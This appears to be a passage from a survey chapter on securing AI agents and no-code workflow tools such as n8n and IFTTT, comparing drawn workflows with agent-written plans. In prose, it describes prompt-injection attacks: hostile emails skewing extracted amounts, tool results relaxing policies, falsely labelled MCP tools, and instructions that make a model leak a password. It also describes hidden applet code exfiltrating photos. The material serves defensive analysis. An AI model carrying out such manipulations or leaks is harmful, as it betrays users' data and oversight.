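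Doshi and colleagues propose deriving rules from a hazard analysis. They adapt System-Theoretic Process Analysis, which engineers use on aircraft and autonomous vehicles to find accidents that interactions between parts could cause even when each part works. For the calendar agent, a developer lists the people affected, such as the user and the other attendees, and what each values. The user values privacy, so a leak of private information is a possible loss. The developer then works out how the agent could cause that loss, for example by mentioning a medical appointment in an email to colleagues, and writes a requirement to prevent it.

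The requirement becomes a rule that software can check: event details must be kept from anyone not attending, anything derived from them must be kept from at least the same people, and no email may contain information that must be kept from its recipient. Doshi and colleagues sort such rules into four groups: those that block an action, those that require it, those that allow it without asking the user, and those that require asking the user. For example, a developer could block private details in emails, require a notice to every attendee, and allow the first notice without confirmation.

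These rules depend on labels, so Doshi and colleagues would extend MCP to make servers label each tool with what it can do, how confidential its data is and how far its output can be trusted. A label can be "unsure", which prompts a question to the user. A company can probably trust the labels on its own tools, but a malicious outside server could label its tools falsely.

Doshi and colleagues tested the idea by modelling the calendar agent in Alloy, a language whose analyser tries every possible run up to a fixed length. The analyser quickly found runs that leaked private data when the model had no rules, but found none once the rules were added. Under the rules, the agent could still reschedule an event and notify the attendees. They tested only a model of the agent, and have yet to build the program that would enforce the rules on real tool calls.

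Hazard analysis takes time and expertise, so several systems have a language model draft the rules instead. AgentCore converts plain-language instructions into Cedar. According to AWS, an analyser can check the resulting policy, and a setting determines whether AgentCore rejects a policy with problems or ignores the findings. An analyser can detect some faults, but it cannot detect that an amount is $500 when the author meant $50.

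A generated rule can inherit the errors of the model that wrote it. In tests of AgentSpec, Wang and colleagues had OpenAI's o1, a 2024 model, write rules from descriptions of the risks and a tenth of the test cases. Its rules caught 87% of the remaining risky programs, but some protected only the system files named in the examples and missed similar ones. A rule meant to stop a household robot from spilling things banned all pouring, including watering a plant. In the driving test, where o1 had no sample cases, its rules prevented violations in five of eight scenarios, while hand-written rules prevented them in all eight.

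The robot results are harder to interpret because the paper gives two figures for the share of risky tasks that the rules stopped. It states this share as 95.56%, but it reports recall, which should measure the same thing, as 70.96%. It also gives 95.56% as the rules' precision, the share of flagged tasks that were really risky.

*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that hostile tool results may lead its update mechanism to relax those policies. Progent's solver prevents unnoticed relaxation, but it only compares each policy with the previous one, so it cannot check whether the initial policy was right.

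Generated rules still have two advantages over letting the model judge each call. The model can write them before it reads any untrusted text, and a person can review them. They help least when the model misunderstands the request. If the same model writes both the plan and the postcondition for deleting two files, it may leave out the frame condition, which requires all other files to stay unchanged. The verifier will then prove that deleting every text file is correct.

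### Checks before and during a run

A check of the whole plan can cover every branch, including those that a particular run never reaches, but it must do so without the values that tools will return. Suppose Michelle's assistant plans to send a summary to whatever address a contact search returns. The verifier can establish that mail text will reach `send_email`, but not whether the address will be outside the company. It can reject the plan, even though the plan may be harmless, or leave the address for a monitor to check during the run. Meijer recommends combining verification with monitoring and compares this to Java, which verifies most properties of a program in advance but checks positions in a list while the program runs.

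A monitor checks the actual address, but by the time it refuses the email, the assistant may already have completed other steps, such as moving a meeting, that someone may have to undo. Noninterference is defined by comparing two runs with different secrets, so a monitor, which observes only one run at a time, cannot establish it just because nothing appears to leak in that run.

Li and colleagues describe a case in which inspecting code in advance is not enough. A mail add-on for an agent always runs the same code, which sends whatever text the model supplies. The model writes that text by following plain-language instructions, which specify a fixed template in a harmless version and require a password to be included in a malicious one. The code and the tool's schema are identical in both versions, and the difference appears only in the text of an actual call, so a reviewer who checks only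 the code and schema cannot approve the harmless version without also approving the malicious one.

A correct decision about a call can become outdated before the call runs. Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) point out in *From Intent to Execution Grant* that the agent may change an argument after approval, or the policy or supporting evidence may change. They propose tying each approval to one exact set of arguments, checking it again when the call runs and letting the agent use it only once. In each of 100 tests of their prototype, 32 simultaneous attempts to use one approval produced exactly one transfer. Without such a safeguard, an agent allowed to pay Acme $480 once might pay it twice. The safeguard works only if the payment service refuses every request without an approval, including requests from an agent that has found other credentials.

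## Graphical tools for connecting services without programming

In a graphical composition system, a person rather than an agent chooses the steps beforehand, by filling in forms or connecting boxes on a canvas. The software then repeats those steps whenever a particular event occurs. These systems were popular well before language models could call tools. By 2018, one of them, IFTTT, had 11 million users and 54 million rules, according to *Decentralized Action Integrity for Trigger-Action IoT Platforms* (Fernandes, Rahmati and colleagues, 2018).

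### Trigger-action rules

IFTTT ("if this then that") lets users make trigger-action rules, which pair an event with a response. One published rule posts on Twitter when the user's Fitbit logs 10,000 steps. To make a rule, the user picks a trigger and an action from lists and fills in details such as an email address or a folder. IFTTT originally called these rules recipes, and since November 2016 it has called them applets.

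Zapier is a similar system aimed at businesses. *IFTTT vs. Zapier* (Rahmati, Fernandes and colleagues, 2017) compares the two as they were in September 2016. An IFTTT rule then had one trigger and one action. Zapier could attach several actions to a trigger and filter events, for instance reacting only to emails with a certain subject. Both systems connect to a service with an OAuth token, a credential the service issues after the user logs in and agrees to the connection. Each platform keeps the token, so it can act later without asking the user again.

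At that time, IFTTT offered 1,239 triggers and 738 actions, or about 914,000 possible pairs. Someone can therefore classify every trigger and action in advance and use the results to check any rule. But both platforms also had a general-purpose option that exchanges web requests with any outside system, and advance classification cannot cover what that system does.

### How an n8n workflow runs

Node-RED, n8n and Langflow replace the single rule with a graph of connected nodes. Each node performs one operation, such as reading a mailbox or testing a condition, and the connections carry data from one node to the next. People use Node-RED largely to connect devices, and Langflow to build applications around language models. Flowise resembles Langflow. Its users can add branches and loops by connecting nodes, and can extend it with scripts, according to *Review of Tools for Zero-Code LLM Based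 Application Development* (Pattnayak and Bohra, 2025).

n8n connects business services, and organisations can run it on their own servers. Tang, Zhou and Chen (2026), in *Characterizing Large Language Model Agentic Workflows*, describe a published n8n workflow that drafts replies to email. Every 15 minutes, a trigger node checks Gmail for new messages. A language model sorts each message into a category, such as high priority, inquiry or billing, and n8n sends it along the connection for that category. A further model call drafts a reply, using a prompt written for the category. The last nodes label the message and save the draft in the original thread, so the user still decides whether to send it.

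n8n stores the drawing as a JSON file. Without the sorting step, and in simplified notation, the file might look like this:

```json
{"nodes": [
   {"name": "New email", "type": "gmailTrigger",
    "parameters": {"everyMinutes": 15},
    "credentials": {"id": "7", "name": "Michelle's Gmail"}},
   {"name": "Write reply", "type": "languageModel",
    "parameters": {"prompt": "Reply politely to: {{ $json.text }}"},
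    "credentials": {"id": "9", "name": "Model account"}},
   {"name": "Save draft", "type": "gmail",
    "parameters": {"operation": "createDraft",
                   "message": "{{ $json.reply }}"},
    "credentials": {"id": "7", "name": "Michelle's Gmail"}}],
 "connections": {
   "New email": ["Write reply"],
   "Write reply": ["Save draft"]}}
```

The trigger node turns each new message into an item, a JSON record with fields for the sender, the subject and the text. n8n passes the items along the connection, and the next node usually runs once for each item. The expression `{{ $json.text }}` inserts the `text` field of the incoming item into the prompt. The model's answer becomes a new item, which the last node saves as a draft.

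The workflow file refers to each credential by number and name but does not contain it. n8n stores the Gmail token encrypted in its own database and uses it when the node contacts Gmail. People can therefore share workflow files without sharing access to their accounts. The language model doesn't receive the token either, so a hostile email cannot make the model reveal it.

### Fixed steps and unlabelled data

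A workflow like this gives much the same protection as a fixed plan in SPA. It is drawn before the emails it processes arrive, and an email cannot add a node or a connection. A hostile email could affect its own category and the wording of the draft, but the workflow has no step that sends mail. *Forms of LLM-Integrated Applications from LLM-Chats to Autonomous AI Agent Systems* (Weber, 2026) uses "workflow" for a sequence of steps that may include conditional branches but that a model does not compose while it runs.

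SPA's planner writes a new plan for each request, whereas a single workflow may handle thousands of messages without further attention from its author. Weber notes that workflows typically run unattended. In some, a person inspects intermediate results, but only at checkpoints.

Most platforms also do not record how secret a value is or how far to trust its source. n8n's connections, for example, carry only the data. If someone connects a mailbox to a payment service, n8n will pass on an account number from a stranger's email just as it would one from an address book. A label check like SPA's would block the payment to the account number from the email.

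The catalogue of operations is also open-ended. n8n has a Code node, in which users write ordinary programs, and an HTTP Request node, which can contact any web address. A reviewer can see from the drawing that data enters a Code node, but has to read the program to learn what happens to it. A workflow without these two nodes is much easier to check.

### Unsafe flows in IFTTT recipes

*Some Recipes Can Do More Than Spoil Your Appetite* (Surbatovich, Aljuraidan and colleagues, 2017) labelled the triggers and actions in published IFTTT recipes by who could learn of each event and who could cause it, then used software to look for flows that broke the label rules. The data, updated from another research team's collection, covered all recipes publicly shared as of May 2016 and contained 19,323 different combinations of trigger and action.

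A recipe that publishes every new phone photo on Flickr breaks the secrecy rule, and could expose a photo of a passport. A recipe that opens a window when the house gets too hot breaks the trust rule, because a burglar could open the window by interfering with the air conditioning. Some labels depended on facts the researchers could not know, such as whether a Google Drive folder was shared, so they counted a recipe as a definite violation only if it broke a rule under every possible label.

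| Result | Share of recipes, all violations | Share of recipes, definite violations |
|---|---|---|
| Breaks only the trust rule | 22.9% | 18.7% |
| Breaks only the secrecy rule | 16.7% | 10.0% |
| Breaks both | 10.3% | 8.4% |
| Total | 49.9% | 37.0% |

A recipe can break a rule without causing harm. The most common breach of the trust rule let a fairly reliable source, such as the *New York Times*, affect something only the user should control, such as a phone's wallpaper. Surbatovich and colleagues examined a random sample of the flagged recipes by hand and judged a little more than a third to be harmless. Most of the others could embarrass the user or reveal personal information. About 13% could cause security problems such as spreading malware, and about 10% could contribute to physical harm.

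One recipe can also trigger another. If one recipe saves every Facebook photo that tags the user to a phone album, and another publishes new photos in that album on Flickr, anyone who can tag the user can publish a photo on the user's Flickr account. IFTTT did not show users these chains. Surbatovich and colleagues had no data on which recipes people used together, so they simulated users' recipe collections. A simulated user with 30 or more recipes had at least one chain on average, and more than half of the chains contained a potentially unsafe recipe.

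Three years later, several of the same researchers studied applets that people had actually installed. *How Risky Are Real Users' IFTTT Applets?* (Cobb, Surbatovich and colleagues, 2020) covers 732 applets belonging to 28 people, who also described how they used them. The automated analysis flagged about 57% of the applets, slightly more than in the first study. After considering the context, the researchers found that just over 3% of all the applets could lead to harm from leaked secrets, and 8.6% posed serious risks from untrusted control. These percentages are rough because the participants were few and came from home-automation forums. Still, a platform that refused every flagged applet would have blocked more than half of these people's automations to stop, at most, about 12% that were risky in these ways. SPA's label checks similarly blocked far more legitimate tasks than attacks.

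The labels also went out of date quickly. Cobb and colleagues had the labels from the first study, but IFTTT had added so many triggers and actions that these covered only about 20% of the participants' applets. Four researchers needed more than six hours of meetings to label everything again. Cobb and colleagues also found a risk that neither kind of label captures. Many applets record the movements of relatives, visitors or neighbours, who may not know that the applet exists. Under the label rules, this is not a violation if the information goes only to the applet's owner.

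### Hidden code in other people's applets

Many people install IFTTT applets made by someone else, who may be dishonest. In *If This Then What?*, Bastys, Balliu and Sabelfeld (2018) studied this threat. An applet can include filter code, a short JavaScript program that runs between the trigger and the action. Users could see which services an applet used, but not its code or hidden settings, and the maker could change both at any time without telling them.

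One popular IFTTT applet, with 97,000 users, backs up iPhone photos to Google Drive. Using their own test accounts, Bastys and colleagues showed that the maker of an applet like this could secretly receive every photo while the backup still worked normally. IFTTT's permissions did not prevent the leak because they controlled which services the applet could use, and the user had approved both services.

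Bastys and colleagues then classified the triggers and actions of 279,828 applets. In 30% of them, the trigger supplied private data and the action offered a way to leak it. These applets had about 8 million users, and 99% of the applets were made by third parties rather than by IFTTT or the services involved. Their makers could use them to steal data, but the study did not find that any had.

As a quick remedy, Bastys and colleagues propose making each applet entirely private or entirely public. The photo backup would be private, so its code could not build a web address that leads to the maker's server. The rule would also block applets that legitimately combine private and public services.

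Their longer-term proposal, FlowIT, tracks private data through the filter code. They prove that it enforces a form of noninterference limited to what the maker's server can observe. In a test on 30 secure and 30 insecure applets, FlowIT caught every insecure one and wrongly blocked one secure one, in which a secret value determined which branch ran but both branches did the same thing. Because IFTTT does not publish filter code, the researchers gathered some of the test programs from forums and recreated others, so the error rate on real applets could be higher.

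FlowIT also has to prevent leaks that involve no private text. Suppose an applet notifies a parent when the children get home, and the notification includes a logo stored on the applet maker's server. When the logo loads, the maker learns that the children have arrived. For triggers like this, where the event itself is private, FlowIT blocks any output that would contact an outside server.

IFTTT acknowledged the design flaw and rated it high severity. Zapier was less exposed because it showed users filter code as a separate step and its staff reviewed code before publishing an automation.

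### When the platform itself is compromised

Even a benign, carefully designed rule depends on the security of the platform that runs it. An attacker who breaks into the platform can steal its OAuth tokens and use them for actions that no user's rule includes. Fernandes and colleagues found that some tokens for popular services gave the platform more access than it needed, which makes such a theft more damaging.

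"Decentralized Action Integrity" gives the example of a rule that turns off the oven when a detector senses smoke. If the platform holds a broad token for the oven, an attacker could also use it to turn the oven on. The paper proposes giving the platform a separate token for each rule, so this rule's token would only permit turning the oven off. The oven's service would also require proof that the smoke detector had gone off recently, and would detect any change to the detector's data along the way. An attacker in control of the platform could then only run rules that users had created, and only after their triggers had occurred.

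The oven's service checks each action itself, so the platform is no longer part of the trusted computing base for actions, but the design does not hide users' data from a compromised platform. *Walnut* (Schoettler, Thompson and colleagues, 2020) describes a later system, modelled on IFTTT, that aims to protect both the data and the correctness of the results. Neither design would help a user whose rule is itself unsafe, such as one that publishes every photo on Flickr, including a photo of a passport.

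### Language models in 6,003 n8n workflows

The IFTTT studies were done before language models spread to these tools. Tang and colleagues examined how people now combine the two. They collected n8n's public workflow templates, kept those that involve a language model, and removed duplicates and drawings with no working steps, leaving 6,003 workflows. They analysed the files without running them.

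A language model sorted the workflows by their main task and agreed with the researchers on 192 of the 200 they checked by hand. Text generation was the most common task, at 31%, followed by information extraction at 18% and multi-step planning or tool use at 17%. In a typical workflow, a language model sits between ordinary steps and turns messy text into something the next node can use. Only 23% of the workflows were chains with no branches or loops.

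Tang and colleagues also traced the connections from each model's output, up to six steps, to any node that acts on an outside service, such as one that sends email or writes to a database.

| Route from the model's output to an outside service | Workflows | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Through a condition, parser or other automatic step | 2,509 | 41.8% |
| Direct | 1,592 | 26.5% |
| No route found | 1,363 | 22.7% |
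| Through a person's approval | 167 | 2.8% |
| Not classified | 372 | 6.2% |

In about 68% of the workflows, then, a model's output could reach an outside service without anyone approving it. This figure may overstate the risk. Many of these actions may be minor, such as posting a summary in the owner's own Slack channel. Templates are also often demonstrations, and a company may add approval steps before using one. On the other hand, the 2.8% may overstate protection, because a workflow with one approved route counted as approved even if its other routes had no approval step.

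The automatic steps in the largest group are not necessarily safety checks, since a step that only tidies the model's output would count. One template that Tang and colleagues describe tracks invoices uploaded to Slack. Software converts the image to text, Claude extracts fields such as the supplier and the amount, and a Code node repairs the format of Claude's answer. The workflow then checks for duplicates, compares the invoice with a database and sends ambiguous cases to a person. These steps catch malformed and repeated entries, but none compares the extracted fields with the original invoice or could detect that a well-formed account number belongs to an attacker.

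Explicit error handling was less common than automatic steps. About 30% of the workflows had some, and in 11% Tang and colleagues could link it to a model's output. Most of it was settings that retry a failed step or let the workflow continue. The researchers counted 2,608 settings that control what happens after an error, most of them on single nodes, and only 111 nodes that deliberately stop the workflow. Continuing is reasonable when a news summary fails, but it is a poor choice when a check on a payment fails.

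In one template with a fuller safeguard, a model improves a submitted draft, and the workflow sends the result to a reviewer by Slack or email. The workflow publishes the result if the reviewer approves it, follows a separate branch if the reviewer rejects it, and alerts a manager if nobody answers in time.

### Agent nodes

In the workflows above, the user who draws the workflow decides when the model runs and what happens to its answer. n8n also has an agent node, which lets the model make some of those decisions. The user attaches a chat model and tools to the node, and possibly a memory of earlier conversations. When data reaches the node, the model chooses its tool calls one at a time, as in an ordinary agent.

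On the canvas, tools are linked to the agent node like other parts of the drawing, but these links only show which tools the agent may use. A drawing of Michelle's email assistant would have an agent node with `fetch_mail` and `send_email` attached. It would look the same whether the agent was summarising her mail or sending it to a stranger, so the mailbox attack works here too.

The rest of the workflow still limits the damage. The agent cannot call a tool that nobody has attached, and its final answer can only go where the connections lead. An author could therefore give the agent only `fetch_mail` and have an ordinary node send the summary to Michelle's own address. A hostile email could then distort the summary but not change where it is sent.

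Many workflow authors build something close to this, probably without security in mind. Tang and colleagues found 8,849 places where a workflow combines a model with other components. About 58% of these combinations had no tools, only a chat model and sometimes a parser that forces its answer into a set format. Such a model resembles SPA's quarantined model, except that n8n does not mark its answer as untrusted. At least 19% included tools.

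People also use n8n to build tools for other agents. The study found 2,916 links that attach a tool to an MCP server inside a workflow, which lets outside agents call the tool. If the workflow's author fixes the recipient in the workflow, the outside agent gets a narrow tool such as `forward_invoice`. Building the tool graphically does not make it safer if it accepts any address.

### Faults in the platform and faults in the drawing

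Some failures come from mistakes in the platform's own code. Bastys and colleagues found that IFTTT's shortened web links, which often led to private files and maps, were easy to guess. Of the 1,000 guesses they tested, 2.5% were real links.

The newer tools have had more serious faults. One in Langflow, CVE-2025-3248, let anyone who could reach a vulnerable server run code on it without logging in. In May 2025, the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency added it to its list of vulnerabilities that attackers are known to exploit. In n8n, CVE-2025-68613 let a logged-in user run code with the same privileges as n8n itself. Another n8n fault, CVE-2026-21858, let outsiders read files on servers running certain workflows with web forms. The developers have released fixes for all three.

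These faults are dangerous partly because such a platform holds credentials for many services. n8n encrypts them in its database but has to be able to decrypt them, so an attacker who controls the software can probably use them all. Fernandes and colleagues propose separate tokens for each rule, which would reduce what such an attacker could do.

A software update can repair faults like these without anyone changing a workflow, but it can't repair a workflow that sends private photos to a public page or pays whatever account number arrives by email, because the platform is running that workflow correctly. Faults in the platform and faults in the workflow are harder to separate where a platform accepts code. The n8n fault that let users run code arose in the expressions they can write in a node's fields, like `{{ $json.text }}` above. n8n evaluates these expressions as JavaScript, so it has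 to restrict what they can do. SPA avoids this problem because the arguments in its plans cannot contain code.

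## Drawn workflows and agent-written plans compared

A person working in n8n and an agent writing a plan for SPA can produce the same sequence of steps. Suppose a company wants to extract the amount due when a supplier's message arrives, record it in a ledger, and alert the accounting department if it exceeds 1,000 euros.

### The supplier's message in both forms

An office manager could draw the task as five connected nodes:

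```text
New supplier message
        |
Extract amount (language model)
        |
Add row to ledger
        |
Amount over 1000?
   |          |
  yes         no
   |          |
 Email      (end)
 accounting
```

An agent given the same instructions could write a plan like this one, which has invented tool names and simplified notation:

```json
{"steps": [
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "read_supplier_message",
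   "inputs": {}, "output": "message"},
  {"type": "q-llm", "inputs": [{"var": "message"}],
   "prompt": "Extract the amount due, in euros.",
   "output_schema": {"amount": "number"}, "output": "bill"},
  {"type": "tool", "tool_name": "add_ledger_row",
   "inputs": {"amount": "bill.amount"}, "output": "row"},
  {"type": "condition", "test": ["gt", "bill.amount", 1000],
   "then": [{"type": "tool", "tool_name": "alert_accounting",
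             "inputs": {"amount": "bill.amount"}, "output": "alert"}],
   "else": []}
]}
```

*SPA*'s language has no step that waits for an event, so a user or another program has to submit the request each time a message arrives. The two versions otherwise match. A program could turn the plan into a drawing by making each step a node and adding an arrow from each step that creates a value to every step that uses it. It could also translate this drawing into a plan, since n8n already stores drawings as JSON.

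The two versions also share a weakness. A hostile message cannot add a step to either, but it can lead the language model to extract 990 euros from a bill for 9,900. Both versions then record the wrong amount and skip the alert. Since the steps are the same, any difference in safety has to come from who wrote them and what software checked them, not from whether they are drawn or written as text.

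### Changing the request

Suppose accounting now wants to hear only about amounts over 2,000 euros. In the drawing, the office manager opens the condition and changes one number. The new limit applies to later messages, and the other steps stay the same.

With the agent, the user changes one number in the request. But SPA calls its planner again for every request, so the model writes a whole new plan, and SPA doesn't check it against the previous one. The new plan might, for example, record only the bills that exceed the limit. A system could avoid this by saving an approved plan and editing only the condition, but it would then work much like n8n.

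A larger change is easier to make with the agent. If some suppliers start billing in dollars, the office manager has to find an exchange-rate service, add a node for it to the drawn workflow and do the multiplication, perhaps in a Code node. With the agent, the user can add "convert dollars to euros first". The planner still needs a tool that does the conversion, because SPA's language has no arithmetic.

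### Who decides, who checks and who answers for mistakes

| | Drawn workflow | Agent-written plan in SPA |
|---|---|---|
| Who chooses the steps | a person, sometimes by copying a template | a model, from the user's request |
| When the steps are fixed | when the person switches the workflow on | anew for each request, before any tool runs |
| Who can read them | people who know the nodes, and programmers where there is code | people who can read JSON, unless software displays it differently |
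| What happens after an error | whatever the author set up | the request ends, and completed steps stay done |
| What a checker can prove | little about secrecy or trust, because values have no labels | that no value breaks the operator's label rules |
| Who answers for a mistake | mainly the author, or whoever switched the workflow on | the user, the operator or the planner's supplier, depending on the mistake |

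Both drawn workflows and agent-written plans need advance planning for exceptions. If a message contains no amount, the quarantined model may invent one to fit the required format. A planner could make the amount optional and use an `exists` test to send incomplete bills to a person. The office manager could draw the same branch, or add it after seeing the first failure, whereas SPA never shows its planner an error.

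The order of the steps also matters, because both versions record the bill before sending the alert. If the ledger is unavailable, SPA ends the request and accounting gets no alert about a bill for 5,000 euros. In n8n, the author can set the workflow to continue after that error.

As with Acme's invoice, a label check would treat the amount as untrusted. The plan passes only if the ledger tool and the alert tool both accept untrusted input. That is reasonable here as long as the server fixes the alert's recipient.

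The same check would work on a drawn workflow if n8n recorded labels. Surbatovich and colleagues checked IFTTT recipes in a similar way. Code inside the workflows is the harder problem. *From Review to Reuse* (Wu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) found a Code node in 54% of 10,803 public n8n templates and an HTTP Request node in 50%.

Responsibility for mistakes is clearer in a drawn workflow. If a condition contains 10,000 instead of 1,000, the person who typed it made the mistake. With an agent, the user may have asked for 1,000 and the planner may have written 10,000. SPA treats the user's request and the operator's settings as trusted, so the user and the operator are responsible for mistakes in them. The user does not approve the plan in SPA, so nobody can catch the planner's own mistakes.

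A formal specification can also shift blame away from the model. In the file-deletion case, Meijer concludes that the model "bears no blame" under the first, incomplete postcondition. On that view, whoever wrote the postcondition made the mistake.

### The same drawing with an agent node

Suppose the office manager replaces everything after the trigger with one agent node, attaches the ledger and email tools, and writes the instructions in the agent's prompt. The drawing is simpler, but it no longer shows whether the agent will record a bill or send the alert, and a hostile message could make the agent skip either step.

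Drawn workflows and agent-written plans are therefore equivalent only when the steps are fixed. Writing the workflow as text would not make it safer, because a step that gave a model the same two tools would be just as open to attack.

The office manager could keep most of the protection by using an agent only to extract the amount and leaving the other steps to ordinary nodes.

Wu and colleagues found n8n's agent node in 34% of the templates. At most that share let a model choose its own tool calls, since an author can use the node without attaching tools. Calling a system a "workflow" also doesn't show whether a model chooses the calls. OpenAI's *Agent Builder*, a guide to the drawing tool of that name, defines a workflow as a combination of agents, tools and control-flow logic.

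### Visual and textual programming in the classroom

A drawing helps a reviewer only if the reviewer understands it. Most of the older evidence comes from teaching and is mixed. *GeckoGraph* (2024), a paper on drawing the types in Haskell programs, summarises studies in which students taught a visual language were more confident, remembered more and enjoyed their courses more than students taught a textual one. It also cites positive results from two teaching tools, Greenfoot and PILeT, that showed pictures alongside text.

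*Visual and Textual Programming Languages* (2017), a literature review, includes evidence for both kinds of language. In one study, 144 volunteers took a four-week online course in either a visual language or C. The researchers concluded from the students' workload that visual programming seemed a good way to introduce the subject. In another study, students who started with a textual language scored significantly better on tests than those who started with a visual one.

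These studies measured how well students learned to program, whereas someone approving an agent's plan has to find mistakes in steps they didn't write.

### Can people find an agent's mistakes in a drawing?

Wu and colleagues tested something closer to that job with Trace2Flow, software that turns the record of an agent's completed run into a graph the user can inspect and edit. Twenty people who used AI agents at least weekly reviewed runs and judged whether the agent had completed the task. In some sessions, they saw only the chat, with the prompt, a progress list and the results. In others, they could also open the graph.

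Participants judged the run correctly in 15 of 23 sessions with the graph and in 7 of 23 without it, a statistically significant difference. With the graph, they also recalled more of the agent's main steps (94% compared with 78%) and answered more questions about the process correctly (82% compared with 57%). The graph helped more with some errors than with others.

| Task | Error | Correct without graph | Correct with graph |
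|---|---|---|---|
| Screening job applicants | the agent accepted a fictional place as European | 2 of 6 | 3 of 6 |
| Sorting news articles | the prompt swapped the two destinations | 1 of 6 | 5 of 6 |
| Listing books | the prompt left out a sheet for non-fiction | 4 of 6 | 5 of 5 |
| Adding new customer reviews | the agent also added reviews already recorded | 0 of 5 | 2 of 6 |

The graph was most useful when the mistake changed the graph's shape. In the book task, participants could see two branches where there should have been three. The graph helped much less with the fictional place, because the steps were correct and the mistake was in a job applicant's CV. By the same logic, a reviewer would probably notice if the supplier workflow had no alert, but the drawing would not show that the model had read 9,900 as 990.

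Accuracy also varied with what participants checked. Those who checked only the final output were right in 1 of 10 sessions, and those who checked only the graph were wrong in both of theirs. Those who compared sources, such as the prompt and the output, were right in 17 of 23. One participant who missed the error in the job-applicant task had seen three CVs and three rows in the results and assumed that the agent had done its work. Participants who compared sources may have been more careful in general, so these figures do not prove that comparing sources improved accuracy.

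A larger limitation of the study is that every run participants judged contained an error, so the right answer was always that the task had failed. If the graph merely made people more suspicious, their scores would have risen too. A follow-up study would need to include correct runs and count false alarms.

The study also provides little evidence about approving a plan in advance, because participants reviewed finished runs with the data and results in front of them. Before a run, a reviewer could look for swapped destinations or a missing branch, but the values would not exist yet. Trace2Flow also uses a language model to reconstruct its graph, and the model may leave something out. A drawing made directly from an SPA plan would show the steps the interpreter will run.

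The participants were also not typical non-programmers, since they were 18 to 32 years old and seven of the 20 had recently built or edited an automated workflow. The study compared having a graph with not having one, so it does not show whether a graph is easier to check than a written list of the same steps.

### Editing a drawing or rewriting a prompt

After each review, participants attempted a related task, such as screening the same applicants for a different job. In some sessions they edited the graph, and in others they wrote a new prompt and could copy from the old one. They succeeded in 17 of 23 sessions with the graph and 13 of 23 with a prompt. None of the differences in success rate, time or perceived difficulty was statistically significant.

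Nine participants preferred the graph, six preferred prompting and five said it depended on the task. Experience seemed to matter, although the groups were small. Six of the seven people with recent workflow experience preferred the graph, compared with three of the other 13. Some newcomers hesitated to change nodes they did not understand. However, five of the six who preferred prompting said they would not prefer it if they had to write the prompt from scratch.

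Several participants found small, local changes easier in the graph and extensive changes easier in a prompt. This matches the supplier example, where a new limit requires editing one node but a new currency requires finding and connecting several nodes.

### LangChain's case against canvas builders

Chase (2025), in *Not Another Workflow Builder*, argues that tools for drawing workflows are still hard for the average non-technical person to use, and that complex tasks soon become an unmanageable mess of nodes and connections. He recommends no-code agents for simple tasks, drawn workflows for moderately complex ones and workflows written in code for complex ones. As models improve, he expects agents and code to take over more of the moderately complex tasks.

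Chase writes for LangChain, which sells tools for building agents and offers LangGraph for writing complex workflows in code, so he has an interest in the conclusion. He presents no usage data. But he names n8n, Flowise and Langflow among the products that solve a real problem for non-technical users, and says that some of these tools build on LangChain's software.

Gopalakrishnan (2026), in *Don't Vibe Code, Do Skele-Code*, also argues that having to learn what a drawing tool's modules do can put off subject experts, though he too is presenting an alternative. The n8n templates suggest that people can manage moderately complex workflows. The median template has 17 nodes, and its longest path has eight steps. But people are more likely to publish workflows they finished, so the templates provide little evidence about those who gave up.

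Older evidence also suggests that visual tools save time. In *Prompt Sapper*, Cheng, Chen and colleagues (2023) had 18 people build services around language models. Participants worked much faster with a visual block tool than in an ordinary programming environment, partly because they did not have to learn how to call each service. The study predates today's coding agents, which can write those calls themselves.

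Chase's scale measures how reliably a system does its job, without accounting for attackers. He would probably class the supplier task as simple and give it to an agent with a prompt and some tools. That agent would be easier to build than the drawing, but it would choose its next call after reading the supplier's message. For tasks like this one, drawing a few nodes is little extra work for fixing the steps in advance.

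### The end of OpenAI's Agent Builder

Chase was responding to Agent Builder, a canvas for drawing workflows that OpenAI had launched the day before. OpenAI's announcement, *Introducing AgentKit* (2025), makes the case for visible steps. In it, the finance company Ramp says the canvas kept its product, legal and engineering teams "on the same page" and shortened its development cycles by 70%. LY Corporation, a Japanese internet company, says engineers and subject experts worked in one interface and had a first workflow running in under two hours. OpenAI chose these testimonials, and neither company describes how it measured the benefit.

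OpenAI announced on 3 June 2026 that it would withdraw Agent Builder, and shut it down on 30 November. OpenAI's *Migrate from Agent Builder* offers customers two replacements: the Agents SDK, for building agents in code, and ChatGPT Workspace Agents, for building them by describing what they should do. This is the squeeze Chase predicted, but Agent Builder is only one product, and OpenAI's notices do not explain the decision.

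The replacements are not equivalent for safety. OpenAI warns that workflows "with strong determinism at their core" may not transfer faithfully to a workspace agent. In the supplier workflow, software compares the amount with 1,000 the same way each time. If the workspace agent only has an instruction to alert accounting about bills over 1,000 euros, a model has to apply the rule, and the supplier's message may influence the model.

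A company can require approval before an agent edits a spreadsheet or sends an email, according to ITPro's *Four things you need to know about OpenAI’s new workspace agents*. In the supplier task, someone would have to approve every ledger entry and every alert, which can cause approval fatigue. Moving the workflow to the SDK would let a developer keep the comparison in ordinary code, but the office manager could no longer change the limit without help.

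### Notebooks for subject experts

Gopalakrishnan, of JPMorgan Chase, proposes a compromise between drawing a workflow and describing it. In his prototype, Skele-Code, a subject expert draws the steps and the connections between them, then describes each step in plain language. A coding agent writes a Python program for each step. The expert can run one step at a time and read its result before continuing, as in the notebooks data analysts use.

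Ordinary software then runs the steps in the order drawn. It calls a model only if a step needs one, for example to summarise a document, or if code fails. The agent may repair the code within a step but cannot add steps or reconnect them. If a bill breaks the extraction step, the agent therefore cannot add a step that sends email, although the repaired code could still do something unexpected.

The expert reads a description of each step and a plain-language report of its result, which the agent's code produces. An expert who approves the workflow has therefore not checked the program that will run. The drawing can also hide decisions, because Skele-Code has no separate node for branches. One step would check whether the bill exceeds 1,000 euros, but the condition for sending the alert would be inside the alert step's own code, so the alert would look unconditional on the canvas. Gopalakrishnan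 presents only the design and has not yet tested it with users.

### Universalis and one plan in several forms

Meijer, in *Unleashing the Power of End-User Programmable AI*, describes a language called Universalis, which machines write and subject experts read. Its programs are paragraphs of ordinary prose with formulas in square brackets. With invented function names, the supplier task might look like this:

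```text
Find the amount due in the supplier's message
[EXTRACT(@message, {... "amount": @amount ...})].
Record it in the ledger [ADD_ROW(@amount)].

- If [@amount > 1000], alert accounting [ALERT(@amount)].
- Otherwise, nothing more is needed.
```

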